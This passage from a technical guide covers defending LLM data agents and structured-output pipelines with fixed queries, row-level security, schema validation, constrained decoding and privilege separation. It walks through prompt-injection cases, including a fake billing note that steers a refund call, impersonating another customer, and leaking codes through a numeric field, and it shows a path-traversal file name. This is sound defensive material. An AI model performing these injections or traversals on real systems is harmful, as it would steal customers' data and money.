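Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Data Agents Under Attack*, tested six systems that answer questions by querying databases, including commercial products from Databricks and Google. In one attack, they planted SQL in table cells and column comments to try to get the agent to copy it into its next query. The attack worked in 24% of attempts on Google's BigQuery but never on Databricks, where the agent often cited a policy when it refused.

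The same attack on DB-GPT, an open-source system, succeeded in 44% of attempts with Claude Sonnet 4.6, 48% with GPT-5.2, and 24% with each of Gemini 3 Flash and DeepSeek V3.2. Each figure comes from only 25 attempts, so the ranking of the models means little, but the rate was not near zero for any of them.

Graph databases, which store records as nodes joined by relationships, have the same problem. The most popular one, Neo4j, uses a query language called Cypher. LangChain's GraphCypherQAChain component asked a model to write Cypher and ran the result. According to NVD's *CVE-2024-8309 Detail*, prompt injection in version 0.2.5 could let an attacker create, change or delete nodes, and could expose one customer's data to another when they shared a database. The entry calls this SQL injection, though Keysight (2025) explains that in Neo4j it takes the form of Cypher injection.

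Red Hat's *CVE-2024-8309* rates the impact as low, partly because the component's documentation required developers to restrict database access. That rating is reasonable for developers who followed the documentation, but not for those who gave the model full control of the database.

### Five defences for one shop

Consider a support assistant for an online shop. Customer 41 signs in and asks for a list of their orders, and the model writes:

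```sql
SELECT id, item, status FROM orders WHERE customer_id = 41;
```

Customer 41 then claims to be customer 57, as in the job-site study, and the model writes the same query with 57 in it. The query looks normal because it is a short SELECT on a table the assistant is supposed to read.

The most effective defence is for the model not to write SQL at all. The developer writes a set of parameterised queries, and the model picks one by name, which a schema can restrict to a list of choices:

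```python
QUERIES = {
    "list_orders": "SELECT id, item, status FROM orders "
                   "WHERE customer_id = %s LIMIT 50",
    "list_returns": "SELECT id, item, reason FROM returns "
                    "WHERE customer_id = %s LIMIT 50",
}
sql = QUERIES[reply["query"]]             # the model picks a name
db.execute(sql, (session.customer_id,))   # the sign-in supplies the number
```

The customer number comes from the sign-in, so nothing typed in the chat can change it. An attacker who fully controls the model's reply can get a list of returns instead of a list of orders, but both lists contain only customer 41's records. A query that takes an order number from the model must still include the `customer_id` condition.

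If the shop wants to allow free-form questions, the program can parse each query before running it. A SQL parser turns the text into a tree showing the type of statement and every table, column and function in it. The program can then accept a single SELECT that uses only the `orders` table and a few functions such as `count` and `sum`, and reject everything else. This stops the model's query from deleting records or reading the staff table. The list of functions matters because a SELECT can, in PostgreSQL for example, call functions that change data. Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues note in *Words Become SQL* (2025) that vulnerability databases already include cases where attackers got past supposedly read-only SQL tools.

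The parser would still accept the query for customer 57, because it uses a permitted table in a permitted way. Query rewriting, the second defence in the 2023 table, replaces `orders` with a smaller query that selects only customer 41's rows, so the model's query runs on those rows alone. The rewriting took about two milliseconds in the researchers' tests, but it works only if the program finds every mention of the table, in whatever form the database accepts. *Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL* (2026) proposes enforcing rules about columns while the model is still generating the query. That could reduce rejected queries, but the database should enforce the rules as well.

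If the parser misses a statement that changes data, the database will still refuse it when the assistant connects through a read-only account. The application uses a separate connection for everything else. The developer can also limit the assistant's account to particular tables and columns. The account can still read customer 57's orders, because the assistant needs access to the whole orders table to serve every customer.

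Row-level security closes this gap in the database itself. The developer attaches a rule to the table, and the database applies it to every query, whoever wrote it. In PostgreSQL the rule could look like this:

```sql
ALTER TABLE orders ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;
CREATE POLICY own_orders ON orders FOR SELECT
  USING (customer_id = current_setting('app.customer_id')::int);
```

The application sets `app.customer_id` from the sign-in before it runs the model's query. If a different customer is signed in, a query for customer 57 returns no rows, because no row can belong to both customers. The job-site chatbot relied on the model to add the customer condition, and a user removed it with one sentence.

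A SELECT can undo this protection by calling a PostgreSQL function that changes such settings, so the parser must block that function. PostgreSQL also exempts the table's owner from the rule by default, so the assistant must connect with a different account. Giving each customer a separate database login is safer, but it is a lot to manage for a shop with thousands of customers. Wang and colleagues found that many systems use one shared account with broad rights, which means the database can't distinguish between users.

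Finally, the database should stop any query that runs too long, and the program should cap the number of rows a query returns. One of the systems in Wang and colleagues' study tried to combine every row of one 13.8-million-row table with every row of another, and stopped responding for 30 minutes because it had no way to cancel the query. A row cap would not have prevented this, since a query can do an enormous amount of work and return a single number. The row cap limits how much a successful attacker can copy at once. A customer can also ask thousands of questions that each take little work to answer, so the assistant needs a limit per user too.

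### Why read-only access still leaks data

A read-only account, which developers often treat as the main safeguard, does not prevent data theft, because theft only requires reading. In the 2023 table, the read-only account stopped every attack that changed the database but neither of the two that read other people's data.

Restricting which rows and columns people can see is harder when they need totals. Wang and colleagues give the example of an analyst who may see total tax by region but not individual records. The analyst asks for the total across all regions, then for the total across all regions except North, where only one taxpayer lives. Subtracting the second total from the first gives that person's exact tax bill. Requiring every total to cover at least, say, 20 people would not help, because both totals cover many more. The system has to track what it has already revealed, or add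 a little random noise to each total. In the researchers' tests, attacks of this kind succeeded in 12% of attempts on BigQuery and 16% to 44% on DB-GPT, depending on the model.

Permitted columns can similarly reveal forbidden ones. Fei, Jiang and colleagues (2026) point out in *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* that someone who can see hourly wages and hours worked can calculate a salary without access to the salary column.

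### Keyword filters and instructions to the model

Searching the query for dangerous words such as DROP, DELETE or UPDATE is simpler than parsing it, but this blocks harmless queries, such as a search for drop earrings or a request for a column called `last_update`. It also misses harmful queries that contain none of the words, such as the query for customer 57 or any SELECT that calls a dangerous function the filter's author did not think of.

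Instructions to the model are unreliable even when nobody is attacking. Fei and colleagues gave 13 models ordinary questions and a description of what data the person asking was allowed to see. The models were supposed to refuse questions that required forbidden data and write queries that followed the access rules for the rest. The table shows how often they wrote queries that broke the rules on two standard sets of questions.

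| Model | BIRD | LiveSQLBench |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 7.7% | 13.3% |
| GPT-5 | 10.5% | 17.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 21.2% | 35.3% |
| Snowflake-R1-7B, a model specialised for SQL | 65.1% | 82.0% |

Models broke the rules more often when a question required combining several tables. Some applied the rules correctly in their reasoning and then wrote a forbidden query. Skill at SQL did not prevent violations, as the last row shows. Fei and colleagues conclude that the database should still enforce access rules itself. Instructions are still useful because a model that follows them can explain to the user why it can't answer, whereas the database would only return an error.

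### What fixed queries cost

A fixed set of queries can't answer a question the developer didn't foresee. Customer 41 might ask which of their orders last winter took longest to arrive, and the assistant would have to say it can't help. The developer can reduce the problem by adding optional parameters to the queries, such as a date range or an order status, and by writing new queries for questions that come up often.

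Limiting a model to fixed queries loses less flexibility than it seems to, because free-form queries are often wrong. In Fei and colleagues' tests, with no access rules, GPT-5's queries returned the right result for 43% of the BIRD questions and 27% of those in LiveSQLBench. These are hard questions, and newer models may do better. But a developer can test a fixed query once and rely on it afterwards, whereas a customer who gets a wrong list of orders from a free-form query may have no way to notice.

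Fixed queries are therefore the better choice for a support assistant, and Pedro and colleagues also put parameterised queries or APIs first in their advice to developers. An analyst's tool has to answer unforeseen questions, so the model must write SQL, and the parser, the read-only account, row-level security and the limits all become necessary. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026) also recommends letting users review and override the generated SQL in fields such as finance and healthcare. This helps an honest analyst catch a mistake or a planted instruction, but it doesn't stop customer 41, who would approve the query.

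## How schemas constrain and check structured output

The shop assistant's fixed queries work only if the program can find a query name in the model's reply. Programs usually prompt the model to reply in JSON, a text format for data. A JSON object is a set of named fields inside braces, and each field holds a string, a number, true, false, null, a list or another object. JSON Schema is a language for describing what a piece of JSON may contain, and each description is called a schema.

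Suppose the shop also uses a model to sort support tickets. The developer might write this schema:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "priority": {"type": "string", "enum": ["low", "high"]},
    "order_id": {"type": "string", "pattern": "^[0-9]{6}$"},
    "summary":  {"type": "string", "maxLength": 200}
  },
  "required": ["priority", "order_id", "summary"],
  "additionalProperties": false
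}
```

| Keyword | What it rules out here |
|---|---|
| `type` | A list instead of an object, or an order number without quotation marks |
| `enum` | Any priority except `low` and `high`, including `urgent` |
| `pattern` | An order number with five digits, or with a command after the sixth |
| `maxLength` | A summary of more than 200 characters |
| `required` | A ticket with no priority |
| `additionalProperties: false` | A ticket with an extra field, such as `refund_approved` |

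JSON Schema allows whatever a schema does not forbid. An empty object passes without `required`, and a ticket can have any number of extra fields without `additionalProperties: false`. Without the `^` and `$` that mark the start and end of the string in the pattern, a validator accepts any text containing six digits in a row. The schema limits the summary to 200 characters but does not restrict its content, so the summary can still contain a harmful link.

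### Checking a finished reply

One way to enforce a schema is to let the model write freely and check the result. The program parses the whole reply as JSON, which fails if the reply contains anything else, such as a greeting before the opening brace. It then runs a validator, a library that compares the parsed data with the schema. If either step fails, the program discards the reply and reports an error or asks the model again.

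Retries work well for a model that usually gets the format right. In *JSONSchemaBench*, Geng, Cooper and colleagues (2025) gave a very small model, Llama 3.2 1B, a short instruction and two examples. Its output followed the schema for 90% of a set of function-call schemas but only 13% of a set of hard schemas from GitHub. If attempts were independent, three tries would raise those figures to 99.9% and 34%. A large current model should do far better, but the program still needs a cap on retries. A ticket that an attacker wrote to break the format will probably break it every time, and each attempt costs money.

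### Blocking invalid tokens

Constrained decoding enforces the schema while the model is writing. At each step the model assigns a probability p(t) to every token t. The software sets m(t) to 1 if the token can still lead to a valid string and to 0 if it can't, and then computes

p'(t) = p(t)m(t) / Σ p(u)m(u)

where the sum runs over every token u in the vocabulary. Multiplying by m removes the invalid tokens, and dividing by the sum makes the remaining probabilities add up to 1 again.

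Suppose the model has reached the value of `priority` and gives `low` a probability of 0.2, `high` 0.1, and all other tokens a combined 0.7. The enum allows only `low` and `high`, so the mask excludes the other tokens. Dividing the two remaining probabilities by their sum, 0.3, gives about 0.67 for `low` and 0.33 for `high`. The model is still twice as likely to write `low` as `high`. If a customer hides an instruction in the ticket that makes `high` more likely, the mask does not reduce that effect.

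The other 0.7 of the probability may have been on words like `unclear`, which the model can no longer write. OpenAI's *Structured outputs* warns that a model will try to fit the schema even when the input is unrelated to it, and may invent content to do so. The ticket schema has this fault because it requires a six-digit order number even when the customer gives none. The developer can fix it by letting `order_id` be null and adding `unknown` to the priorities.

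### From finite automata to current engines

To compute the mask, the software needs to know which tokens are valid at each point. *Efficient Guided Generation for Large Language Models* (2023), by Willard and Louf, describes how to find them with a finite automaton, a machine with a fixed set of states that moves between them as it reads characters. For the order number, the state is the number of digits the model has written. After four digits, a token with one or two digits is valid, but a three-digit token is not, because no valid order number begins with seven digits.

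Tokens and characters don't correspond one to one, as *SGLang* (2023) explains, so the software has to trace each token through the automaton one character at a time. Willard and Louf's algorithm does this once in advance for the whole vocabulary and records which tokens the automaton can read from each state. During generation, the software only looks up the current state. It must also exclude tokens that lead to a dead state, which *Automata-Based Steering of Large Language Models for Diverse Structured Generation* (2025) defines as one with no path to an accepting state.

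Willard and Louf asked GPT-2 medium, an early model, when Noam Chomsky was born, and the output was "about 1895". They then added a pattern that required 19 followed by two digits, which rules out 1895 but allows any year from 1900 to 1999. Chomsky was born in 1928, but the pattern accepts 1952 just as readily.

A finite automaton can't track brackets nested to arbitrary depth, because it has a fixed number of states. *XGrammar* (2024) describes an engine that uses pushdown automata, which add a stack. The engine puts an item on the stack when a bracket opens and removes it when the bracket closes. Because a token's validity can now depend on the stack, the masks are harder to prepare in advance. XGrammar sorts tokens into those that are always valid at a given position, those that never are, and those whose validity depends on the stack, so it only has to check the last group during generation.

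Newer engines prepare most schemas quickly, and *XGrammar-2* (2026) reports compiling most JSON schemas within a millisecond. Complicated schemas can still be slow to compile. Anthropic's *Structured outputs* estimates that each optional field roughly doubles part of the grammar, and Anthropic's service allows at most 24 optional fields per request.

Even a correct mask doesn't guarantee that the model finishes. A model can keep opening new lists or nested objects, each a valid step, until it runs out of tokens. *Stay Within Your Bounds* (2026) raised the limit from 512 to 4,096 tokens in its JSON tests, but schema validity stayed well below 100% for every method and model. It proposes steering the model towards the nearest valid ending. OpenAI describes a similar failure in its older JSON mode, which guarantees valid JSON but no particular schema. If the prompt doesn't ask for JSON, the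 model may write whitespace until it reaches the token limit.

### How well engines follow schemas

Geng and colleagues tested six engines on a collection of 9,558 real schemas, leaving out the easiest and hardest groups. They measured how many schemas each engine accepted and how often the output then followed the schema. The table shows two of their eight sets.

| Engine | Function-call schemas accepted | Output followed the schema | Hard GitHub schemas accepted | Output followed the schema |
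|---|---|---|---|---|
| None (model alone) | 100% | 90% | 100% | 13% |
| Guidance | 98% | 98% | 60% | 69% |
| llama.cpp | 98% | 97% | 61% | 63% |
| Outlines | 99% | 96% | 47% | 6% |
| XGrammar | 100% | 93% | 69% | 41% |
| OpenAI | 89% | 100% | 9% | 100% |
| Gemini | 86% | 100% | Under 1% | Not reported |

The two commercial services rejected most of the hard schemas, and OpenAI's output matched every schema it accepted. These services ran their own, larger models, so their results aren't directly comparable with the others. Outlines did badly mainly because it often exceeded a 40-second time limit. The researchers generated one output per schema, so a score of 100% means only that they saw no failures. They published the benchmark through the Guidance project, whose engine did best among the open ones.

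Constraints can speed up generation or slow it down. On the easy GitHub schemas, the model alone took about 16 milliseconds per token, compared with 40 for Outlines, 27 for llama.cpp and 7 for Guidance. Guidance saves time by filling in text that the schema fully determines, such as field names, without running the model for each token.

For security, the most important failure is an engine that accepts a schema and then allows output that breaks it. Geng and colleagues tested for this with the official JSON Schema test suite, which covers 45 groups of features. XGrammar allowed invalid output in 38 groups and failed to compile schemas in three, while Guidance allowed invalid output in one group and failed to compile schemas in 25. A compile error is better for a program that relies on the constraint, because the developer finds out at once. An engine that allows invalid output may seem to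 work for months, because the model usually writes valid output anyway, until someone sends input designed to make it write invalid output.

These figures date from January 2025, but the problem persists. *DConstrain* (October 2026) found 124 schemas in the same collection for which XGrammar accepted a complete JSON text that broke the schema. For one schema that requires an object, the engine accepted the number 0. The study searched specifically for failures, so the count does not show how often they occur. Engines can also be too strict. *STAGE* (2026) trained a model to write JSON from source documents, and adding XGrammar lowered schema validity by four points. The paper attributes the drop to the grammar blocking correct tokens that the model would otherwise have produced.

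### Whether constraints make answers worse

*Let Me Speak Freely?* (Tam et al., 2024) started a long debate by reporting that strict formats can hurt a model's reasoning. The effect varied by task. On DDXPlus, a set of medical diagnosis questions, Gemini 1.5 Flash did much better when it had to answer in JSON, perhaps because the format limited the possible answers.

Will Kurt, whose company develops Outlines, replied that the losses came from poor prompts and badly designed schemas. Geng and colleagues followed Kurt's setup on three reasoning tasks with Llama 3.1 8B, and no engine did worse than the unconstrained model. Guidance did best, raising accuracy on school maths problems from 80.1% to 83.8%. Field order matters too. Castillo's *The good, the bad, and the ugly of Gemini’s structured outputs* found that Google's service sorted the fields alphabetically in all 100 test schemas. That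 would put `answer` before `reasoning`, so the model would have to answer before working through the problem.

Later studies tried to separate the effect of asking for a format from the effect of masking tokens, and they disagree. Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick (2026), in *The Format Tax*, tested ten models and attribute most of the loss in accuracy to the request. Among the six open models, asking for a format lowered accuracy by 3.9 points on average, and masking lowered it by another 1.6. *The Hidden Cost of Structured Generation in LLMs* (2026) made a similar comparison on maths problems and attributes most of the loss to masking, particularly when the permitted tokens had a low probability before masking.

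Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026), in *Constrained Decoding*, offer a proof that masking can't lower the probability of the correct answer, provided the prompt and expected format stay the same and the schema permits that answer. The formula divides by a sum of at most 1, which can't make a number smaller. If `low` is correct in the ticket example, masking raises its probability from 0.2 to 0.67. In one of their experiments, a second model extracted the answers to a letter puzzle from reasoning that was already complete. Constraining that step raised accuracy by about three to six points for all six models.

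The proof assumes that the reasoning is fixed before the constraint begins. Nguyen and colleagues accept that constraining the reasoning too can help or hurt. The proof also counts any answer in the wrong format as wrong. Geng and colleagues give a hypothetical case in which a model is about to write 89,000 where the schema allows only digits. The mask blocks the comma, and the model writes 890000 instead. Under the proof's assumptions this loses nothing, because both answers count as wrong. But 89,000 would have caused an error that the program could catch, while 890000 is a wrong number that passes every check.

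Although they disagree, Lee and colleagues and *The Hidden Cost of Structured Generation in LLMs* make much the same recommendation, to let the model reason freely and impose the format afterwards. Anthropic's service already does this for models that think before answering, because the grammar applies only to the final reply. Three of the newer commercial models that Lee and colleagues tested lost almost nothing when asked for a format, but one of them, GPT-5.4 nano, lost 59 points on maths when the service enforced XML, and gained two with JSON. The loss probably matters most for very small models, for which *The Constraint Tax* (2026) describes the worrying result as "wrong answer, valid schema". Newer benchmarks such as *The Structured Output Benchmark* (2026) therefore score validity separately from the accuracy of the values.

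### What providers enforce

No major provider enforces all of JSON Schema. The table shows how each provider handles the ticket schema, according to Anthropic's and OpenAI's documentation and Google's *Structured outputs*.

| Keyword | Anthropic | OpenAI | Google |
|---|---|---|---|
| `enum` | Supported, but capital letters may differ | Supported | Supported |
| `additionalProperties: false` | Compulsory | Compulsory | Supported |
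| `pattern` | Simple patterns | Supported, except on fine-tuned models | Not on the list |
| `maxLength` | Causes an error | Not on the list | Not on the list |

Some strict modes return an error when a schema contains something they can't enforce. Anthropic's service does this for `maxLength`, `minimum` and similar keywords, and OpenAI's does it for any schema it doesn't support. A limit is more likely to be lost in the helper libraries that developers use to send the schema. Most of Anthropic's helpers remove an unsupported keyword and write the limit into the field's description, which the model may not follow. Some helpers then check the reply against the original schema, but the TypeScript helper `jsonSchemaOutputFormat()` does not. Whoever writes the schema can steer the model through its field names, descriptions and permitted values, so schemas must come from trusted code.

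Some replies don't follow the schema. If Claude refuses a request, the HTTP request still succeeds, but the reply has a stop reason of `refusal` and may contain a message instead of the JSON. OpenAI puts the message in a separate `refusal` field. The example refusal in OpenAI's *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* has the ordinary finish reason, `stop`, so a program that checks only the finish reason would miss the refusal. A reply that reaches the token limit is cut off, even if the JSON is incomplete, and has a stop reason of `max_tokens` from Anthropic or a finish reason of `length` from OpenAI's Chat Completions API.

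Anthropic also does not guarantee the capitalisation of enum values, so a model might return `Needs Review` where the schema has `Needs review`, with no error. A lookup table with no such entry will then raise an error, but code that closes every ticket not marked `Needs review` will close this one.

The application therefore has to validate every reply again against the full schema, even when it uses a strict mode. Google also tells developers in its documentation to always validate values. The second check takes little compute and doesn't depend on the provider, the engine or the helper library. OpenAI recommends generating the schema from the program's own data types, or the data types from the schema, so that the two stay consistent.

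### When parsing goes wrong

A validator sees only what the parser gives it, so the parser has to be strict as well. In Python, the whole check could look like this:

```python
def unique_keys(pairs):
    fields = dict(pairs)
    if len(fields) != len(pairs):
        raise ValueError("duplicate key")
    return fields

if refused or cut_off or len(text) > 5000:
    raise ValueError("unusable reply")
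ticket = json.loads(text, object_pairs_hook=unique_keys)
jsonschema.validate(ticket, TICKET_SCHEMA)
```

Many developers use a repair library, which accepts broken JSON and guesses what the model meant. The guess is often right when the only fault is a missing comma, but guessing is dangerous when the reply was cut off. Suppose a model is writing an instruction to delete records older than 365 days and reaches its token limit after the 3. The library adds the missing brace, and the result is a valid instruction to delete records older than 3 days. Tools that take the first JSON object they find in a reply have a different weakness. If the model quotes a customer's message, the first object may be one that the customer wrote.

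Two parsers can also read the same text differently. The JSON standard recommends, but does not require, that each key appear only once in an object. Given `{"priority": "low", "priority": "high"}`, Python's parser keeps the last value, while some others keep the first. If one service checks the ticket and another acts on it, the first may approve `low` and the second act on `high`. The database CouchDB had a flaw of this kind in 2017 (CVE-2017-12635). Its two parsers handled a repeated `roles` field differently, which could let an ordinary user become an administrator. The code above rejects duplicate keys. The program should also serialize the data it checked and pass that on instead of the model's original text.

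Smaller differences between implementations can also let invalid values through. Python's JSON parser accepts `NaN` ("not a number"), which is not valid JSON. `NaN` is neither greater nor less than any number, so a refund of `NaN` can pass both a minimum and a maximum check. In Python regular expressions, `$` also matches just before a final line break, so a Python validator may accept an order number that ends with one.

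Extra fields do harm when a program copies everything it receives. If the ticket system saves each field of the reply into the matching database column, a reply with `"refund_approved": true` approves a refund that nobody reviewed. Some libraries rebuild a program object when they find particular extra keys. Setting `additionalProperties` to false blocks such fields, but it applies only to the object where it appears, so the developer has to repeat it in every nested object. The program should also copy only the fields it needs, by name, which keeps the extra ones out even if someone later loosens the schema.

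## What schema-valid output can still do

Suppose the shop lets its support assistant issue refunds. The refund tool takes an order number, an amount and a reason, and the program validates every call against a strict schema. Customer 41, who paid 40 for a lamp, writes that it arrived broken. Below the complaint, the ticket has a paragraph laid out like a note from the shop's billing team, with a friend's order number and a much larger amount. The model follows the note and produces this call:

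```json
{"order_id": "204518", "amount": 4000, "reason": "Arrived damaged"}
```

The call should have used customer 41's own order, 104233, and an amount of 40. It still passes validation, because the order number has six digits, the amount is a number and the reason is a short string. A maximum amount in the schema would not help much. The shop sells some things for 4,000, so a limit low enough to stop this call would also block legitimate refunds.

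The program can catch the call by comparing it with the shop's records:

```python
order = find_order(call["order_id"])
amount = call["amount"]
if order is None or order.customer_id != session.customer_id:
    raise Refused("not this customer's order")
if not 0 < amount <= order.paid - order.refunded:
    raise Refused("more than the customer paid")
if amount > 100:
    return ask_staff(order, amount)
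refund(order, amount)
```

The customer number comes from the sign-in, as in the fixed queries. The program refuses this call because order 204518 belongs to someone else. If the note had named customer 41's own order, the program would still have refused to refund 4,000 for a lamp that cost 40. Subtracting earlier refunds stops a customer from collecting the same money twice, but the program has to run the check and the refund in one database transaction, because otherwise two identical calls that arrive together could both pass. The program refunds the card used for the purchase, so the tool doesn't need a destination field.

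A member of staff approves any refund above 100. The approval screen should take its figures from the database, because an attacker may have written the reason given for the refund. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, doubts that approval works well as a general defence, since people who see many requests learn to click "OK" as fast as possible. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, suggest matching the approval step to the risk, with no prompt for reading open data, a light confirmation for changes to the user's own files, and multi-factor approval for payments and other irreversible actions.

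### Form, meaning and authority

A schema checks only the form of a call, not its meaning or authority. Meaning concerns whether the values match the facts, such as whether order 204518 exists and how much the buyer paid. Authority depends on who is asking. The friend may have a good claim to a refund on that order, but customer 41 can't make it for them.

The program can move part of the authority check into the schema by generating a schema for each ticket, with an enum that lists only that customer's orders. Constrained decoding then limits the model to those orders. The program still has to validate the reply and check the amount, because the maximum refund depends on which order the model picks.

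*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* describes the same risk in a furniture shop's chatbot, where a user might get the model to return another customer's order. The paper recommends asking for the user's credentials when the model attempts the return, or blocking access to other customers' data for the whole session.

These checks can't establish whether the lamp arrived broken. A refund of 40 on order 104233 would pass them all even if customer 41 had made up the story, though the customer could also have told it to a person.

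### How much each field can carry

One way to compare field types is to count the messages an attacker could send through each. An enum with k values allows k different messages, or at most log₂ k bits of information. The table shows the same calculation for other fields.

| Field | Possible values | Bits, at most |
|---|---|---|
| Priority, `low` or `high` | 2 | 1 |
| Refund reason from a list of eight | 8 | 3 |
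| Six-digit order number | 1,000,000 | 19.9 |
| List of exactly 20 reasons, each from the list of eight | 8²⁰ | 60 |
| 64-bit whole number | 2⁶⁴ | 64 |
| 200 characters of plain English text | 95²⁰⁰ | 1,314 |

A six-digit order-number field has room for about 20 bits, enough to hold the six-digit login codes that many services send by email. If a poisoned message causes an email assistant to put a login code in that field, and the attacker can see the result, the code leaks in a value that looks like any other order number. JSON sets no limit on the length of a number, so an integer field without a maximum can carry as much as a text field. A 500-digit integer has room for about 200 characters. Capacity also adds up over repeated calls, and a thousand yes-or-no answers can carry 125 characters.

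Limiting how much information the output can carry does not necessarily limit the damage it can do. If a program pays out whenever the model writes `"approved": true`, an attacker needs to control only that one bit. A developer therefore has to consider what the program will do with each permitted value, as well as how many values there are.

Free-text fields carry the most risk. The `reason` field could hold a link for a member of staff to click, a script that runs in the staff dashboard if the program doesn't escape it, or another injection for the next model that reads it. Willison warns that when one model's output is fed into another, a malicious prompt can make the first model repeat the attack in its answer. A summary of an untrusted document is therefore still untrusted. If the program needs only a category, the developer should replace the text field with an enum.

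### Addresses, paths and references

Some strings are dangerous because of what they point to. A valid web address can still lead to an attacker's server and carry private data at its end, so the program has to restrict where addresses can lead and where they can come from.

A file path in the model's output can point outside the intended folder. This flaw is called path traversal, and OWASP lists it among the results of unchecked model output. If a program adds the model's file name to `/uploads/41/`, the name `../57/passport.pdf` leads to another customer's folder. The program should resolve the full path, including any symbolic links, and then confirm that it is still inside the intended folder.

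The program should check that an email's recipient is allowed by comparing the whole address with the user's contacts or the company's records. Accepting any address in the same organisation stops data from leaving it, but *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* points out that an attacker could still have the assistant email a coworker and ask them to approve something or ignore an alert.

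It is safer for the model to choose a reference and for the program to look up the value. For example, the model picks contact 3 or file 7 from a numbered list of items this user may use, and the program finds the address or path. An attacker can then make the model choose the wrong item but can't add one to the list.

References are even more useful for secrets, since a model can't leak a password it never received. Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, tested a product from their own company in which the model names a connection, such as the one to GitHub, and trusted software adds the access key to the outgoing request. All 16 probes had the expected security result. A request to GitHub succeeded, and the key did not appear in the sandbox's environment variables, in the file locations they searched or in requests to other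 sites. A second connection failed because the software put the key in the wrong part of the request, but this did not expose the key.

The vendor's test is small and covers only theft of the key. An agent without the key can still delete a repository through the trusted software if the key's permissions allow it. Kenney and colleagues conclude that the software also needs rules about which actions it will perform.

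### Data that turns back into program objects

Programs often save their internal objects as structured data and rebuild them later. If model output can have the same format as a saved object, an attacker can choose which objects the program builds.

Until December 2025, LangChain could load an attacker's data as one of its own saved objects, which it marks with a key called `lc`. According to MITRE's *CVE-2025-68664* (2025), the functions that save data, `dumps()` and `dumpd()`, did not escape ordinary data that contained the same key. Positive Technologies' *Langchain · Langchain · CVE-2025-68664* notes that an attacker could exploit this with a prompt injection that shapes the model's response. The attack takes effect when the application loads the stored text, much as in second-order SQL injection.

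The main danger was theft of environment variables, where many applications keep passwords and access keys. Red Hat's *CVE-2025-68664* describes a more severe result, arbitrary code execution. The score of 9.3 out of 10 in OSV's *CVE-2025-68664* (2025) fits theft better, because it is based on a high impact on confidentiality but only a low impact on system integrity. LangChain fixed the flaw in versions 0.3.81 and 1.2.5.

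A schema that forbids extra fields would reject an unexpected `lc` key, but if even one field accepts any object, the key can appear inside that object. Programs should save model output as plain data, never in Python's `pickle` format, because loading a pickle can run code.

### Two models with a barrier between them

Types can also protect one model from another. An email assistant is vulnerable because the model that reads strangers' messages is also the one that calls the tools. Willison's dual-LLM pattern divides the work. A privileged model takes requests from the user and can call tools. A quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools. An ordinary program, the controller, stores all the text and gives the privileged model only names for it. Summarising an email works like this:

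1. The privileged model asks for the latest email. The controller fetches it, stores it as `$VAR1` and gives the model that name.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller sends the email to the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`.
3. The privileged model asks the controller to display `$VAR2`, and the controller puts the summary on the user's screen.

An instruction hidden in the email reaches only the quarantined model, which can't act on it. The privileged model never sees the quarantined model's output, with one exception that Willison allows. If the quarantined model must pick from a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that the answer is in the set and pass it to the privileged model.

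Willison proposed this in April 2023 without an experiment, so it has no measured attack success or task loss. He called the solution "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and worse to use, and a single mistake that lets text through removes the protection. The solution also assumes that the user's request is safe, which is false if someone tricks the user into pasting an attacker's text.

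A more basic flaw emerged two years later. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested in a meeting, and the meeting notes contain Bob's address and the document's name. The privileged model makes the right plan without seeing the notes. But the quarantined model has to find the address, and an instruction in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead. The controller then sends the right document to the wrong person. As in the refund example, the barrier protects the choice of actions but not the values that go into them. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives a formal example of a related leak, in which the quarantined model copies notes into a reply that the plan then sends.

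### Numbers and categories in place of text

The strict version of the pattern is useless when the privileged model has to decide something from the untrusted text. A bug-fixing agent can't do much if it never learns what the bug report says. Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, extend Willison's exception into a general method. The quarantined model may pass on whole numbers, decimal numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a fixed list, or short lists of these, but no free text. They built three agents this way:

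- A shopping agent reads product reviews. The quarantined model gives each review two scores from 0 to 10, one for how strongly it supports the product and one for relevance, and the privileged model sees the median scores and the number of reviews.
- A calendar agent arranges meetings by email. The quarantined model turns the other person's messages into a list of time slots from a fixed set.
- A coding agent fixes bugs. The quarantined model passes on a bug category, the numbers of suspicious files in a sorted list, and line numbers. The program replaces each file number with the path.

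The tests used 500 shopping requests, 100 pairs of simulated people with calendars, and 180 real bug reports. In the attacks, a review contained an instruction for the agent to leave the page, a correspondent demanded the user's calendar, and a bug report included a request for an extra file.

| Agent | Tasks solved, ordinary design | Tasks solved, restricted types | Attack success, ordinary design | Attack success, restricted types |
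|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping (GPT-4o) | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar (GPT-4o) | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing (GPT-5.2) | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The shopping and scheduling agents lost no performance, because a few numbers or time slots contain everything they need from the untrusted text. The bug-fixing agent lost about a third of its fixes, because bug reports often explain the problem in ways that a category and some line numbers can't. The attack success rates of zero are weaker evidence of security than they seem, since each agent faced only one fixed attack. The design is stronger evidence because it gives an attacker no field to write an instruction in.

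That argument holds only if the numbers are limited too, because a long enough integer can encode a sentence. Jacob and colleagues cap the length of lists for this reason, and their review scores have a narrow range, but their general rule allows any integer. They also exclude deception from their threat model. A bug report could still name a working permission check as the faulty code, and the coding agent might then change it. The method also needs at least two agents and a carefully designed set of fields for each task.

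FIDES, a Microsoft system, has a similar option. According to *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), it can let true-or-false values and choices from a list bypass its rules because they can carry only limited influence, but FIDES's own evaluation was run with the option off.

### Six patterns for narrower agents

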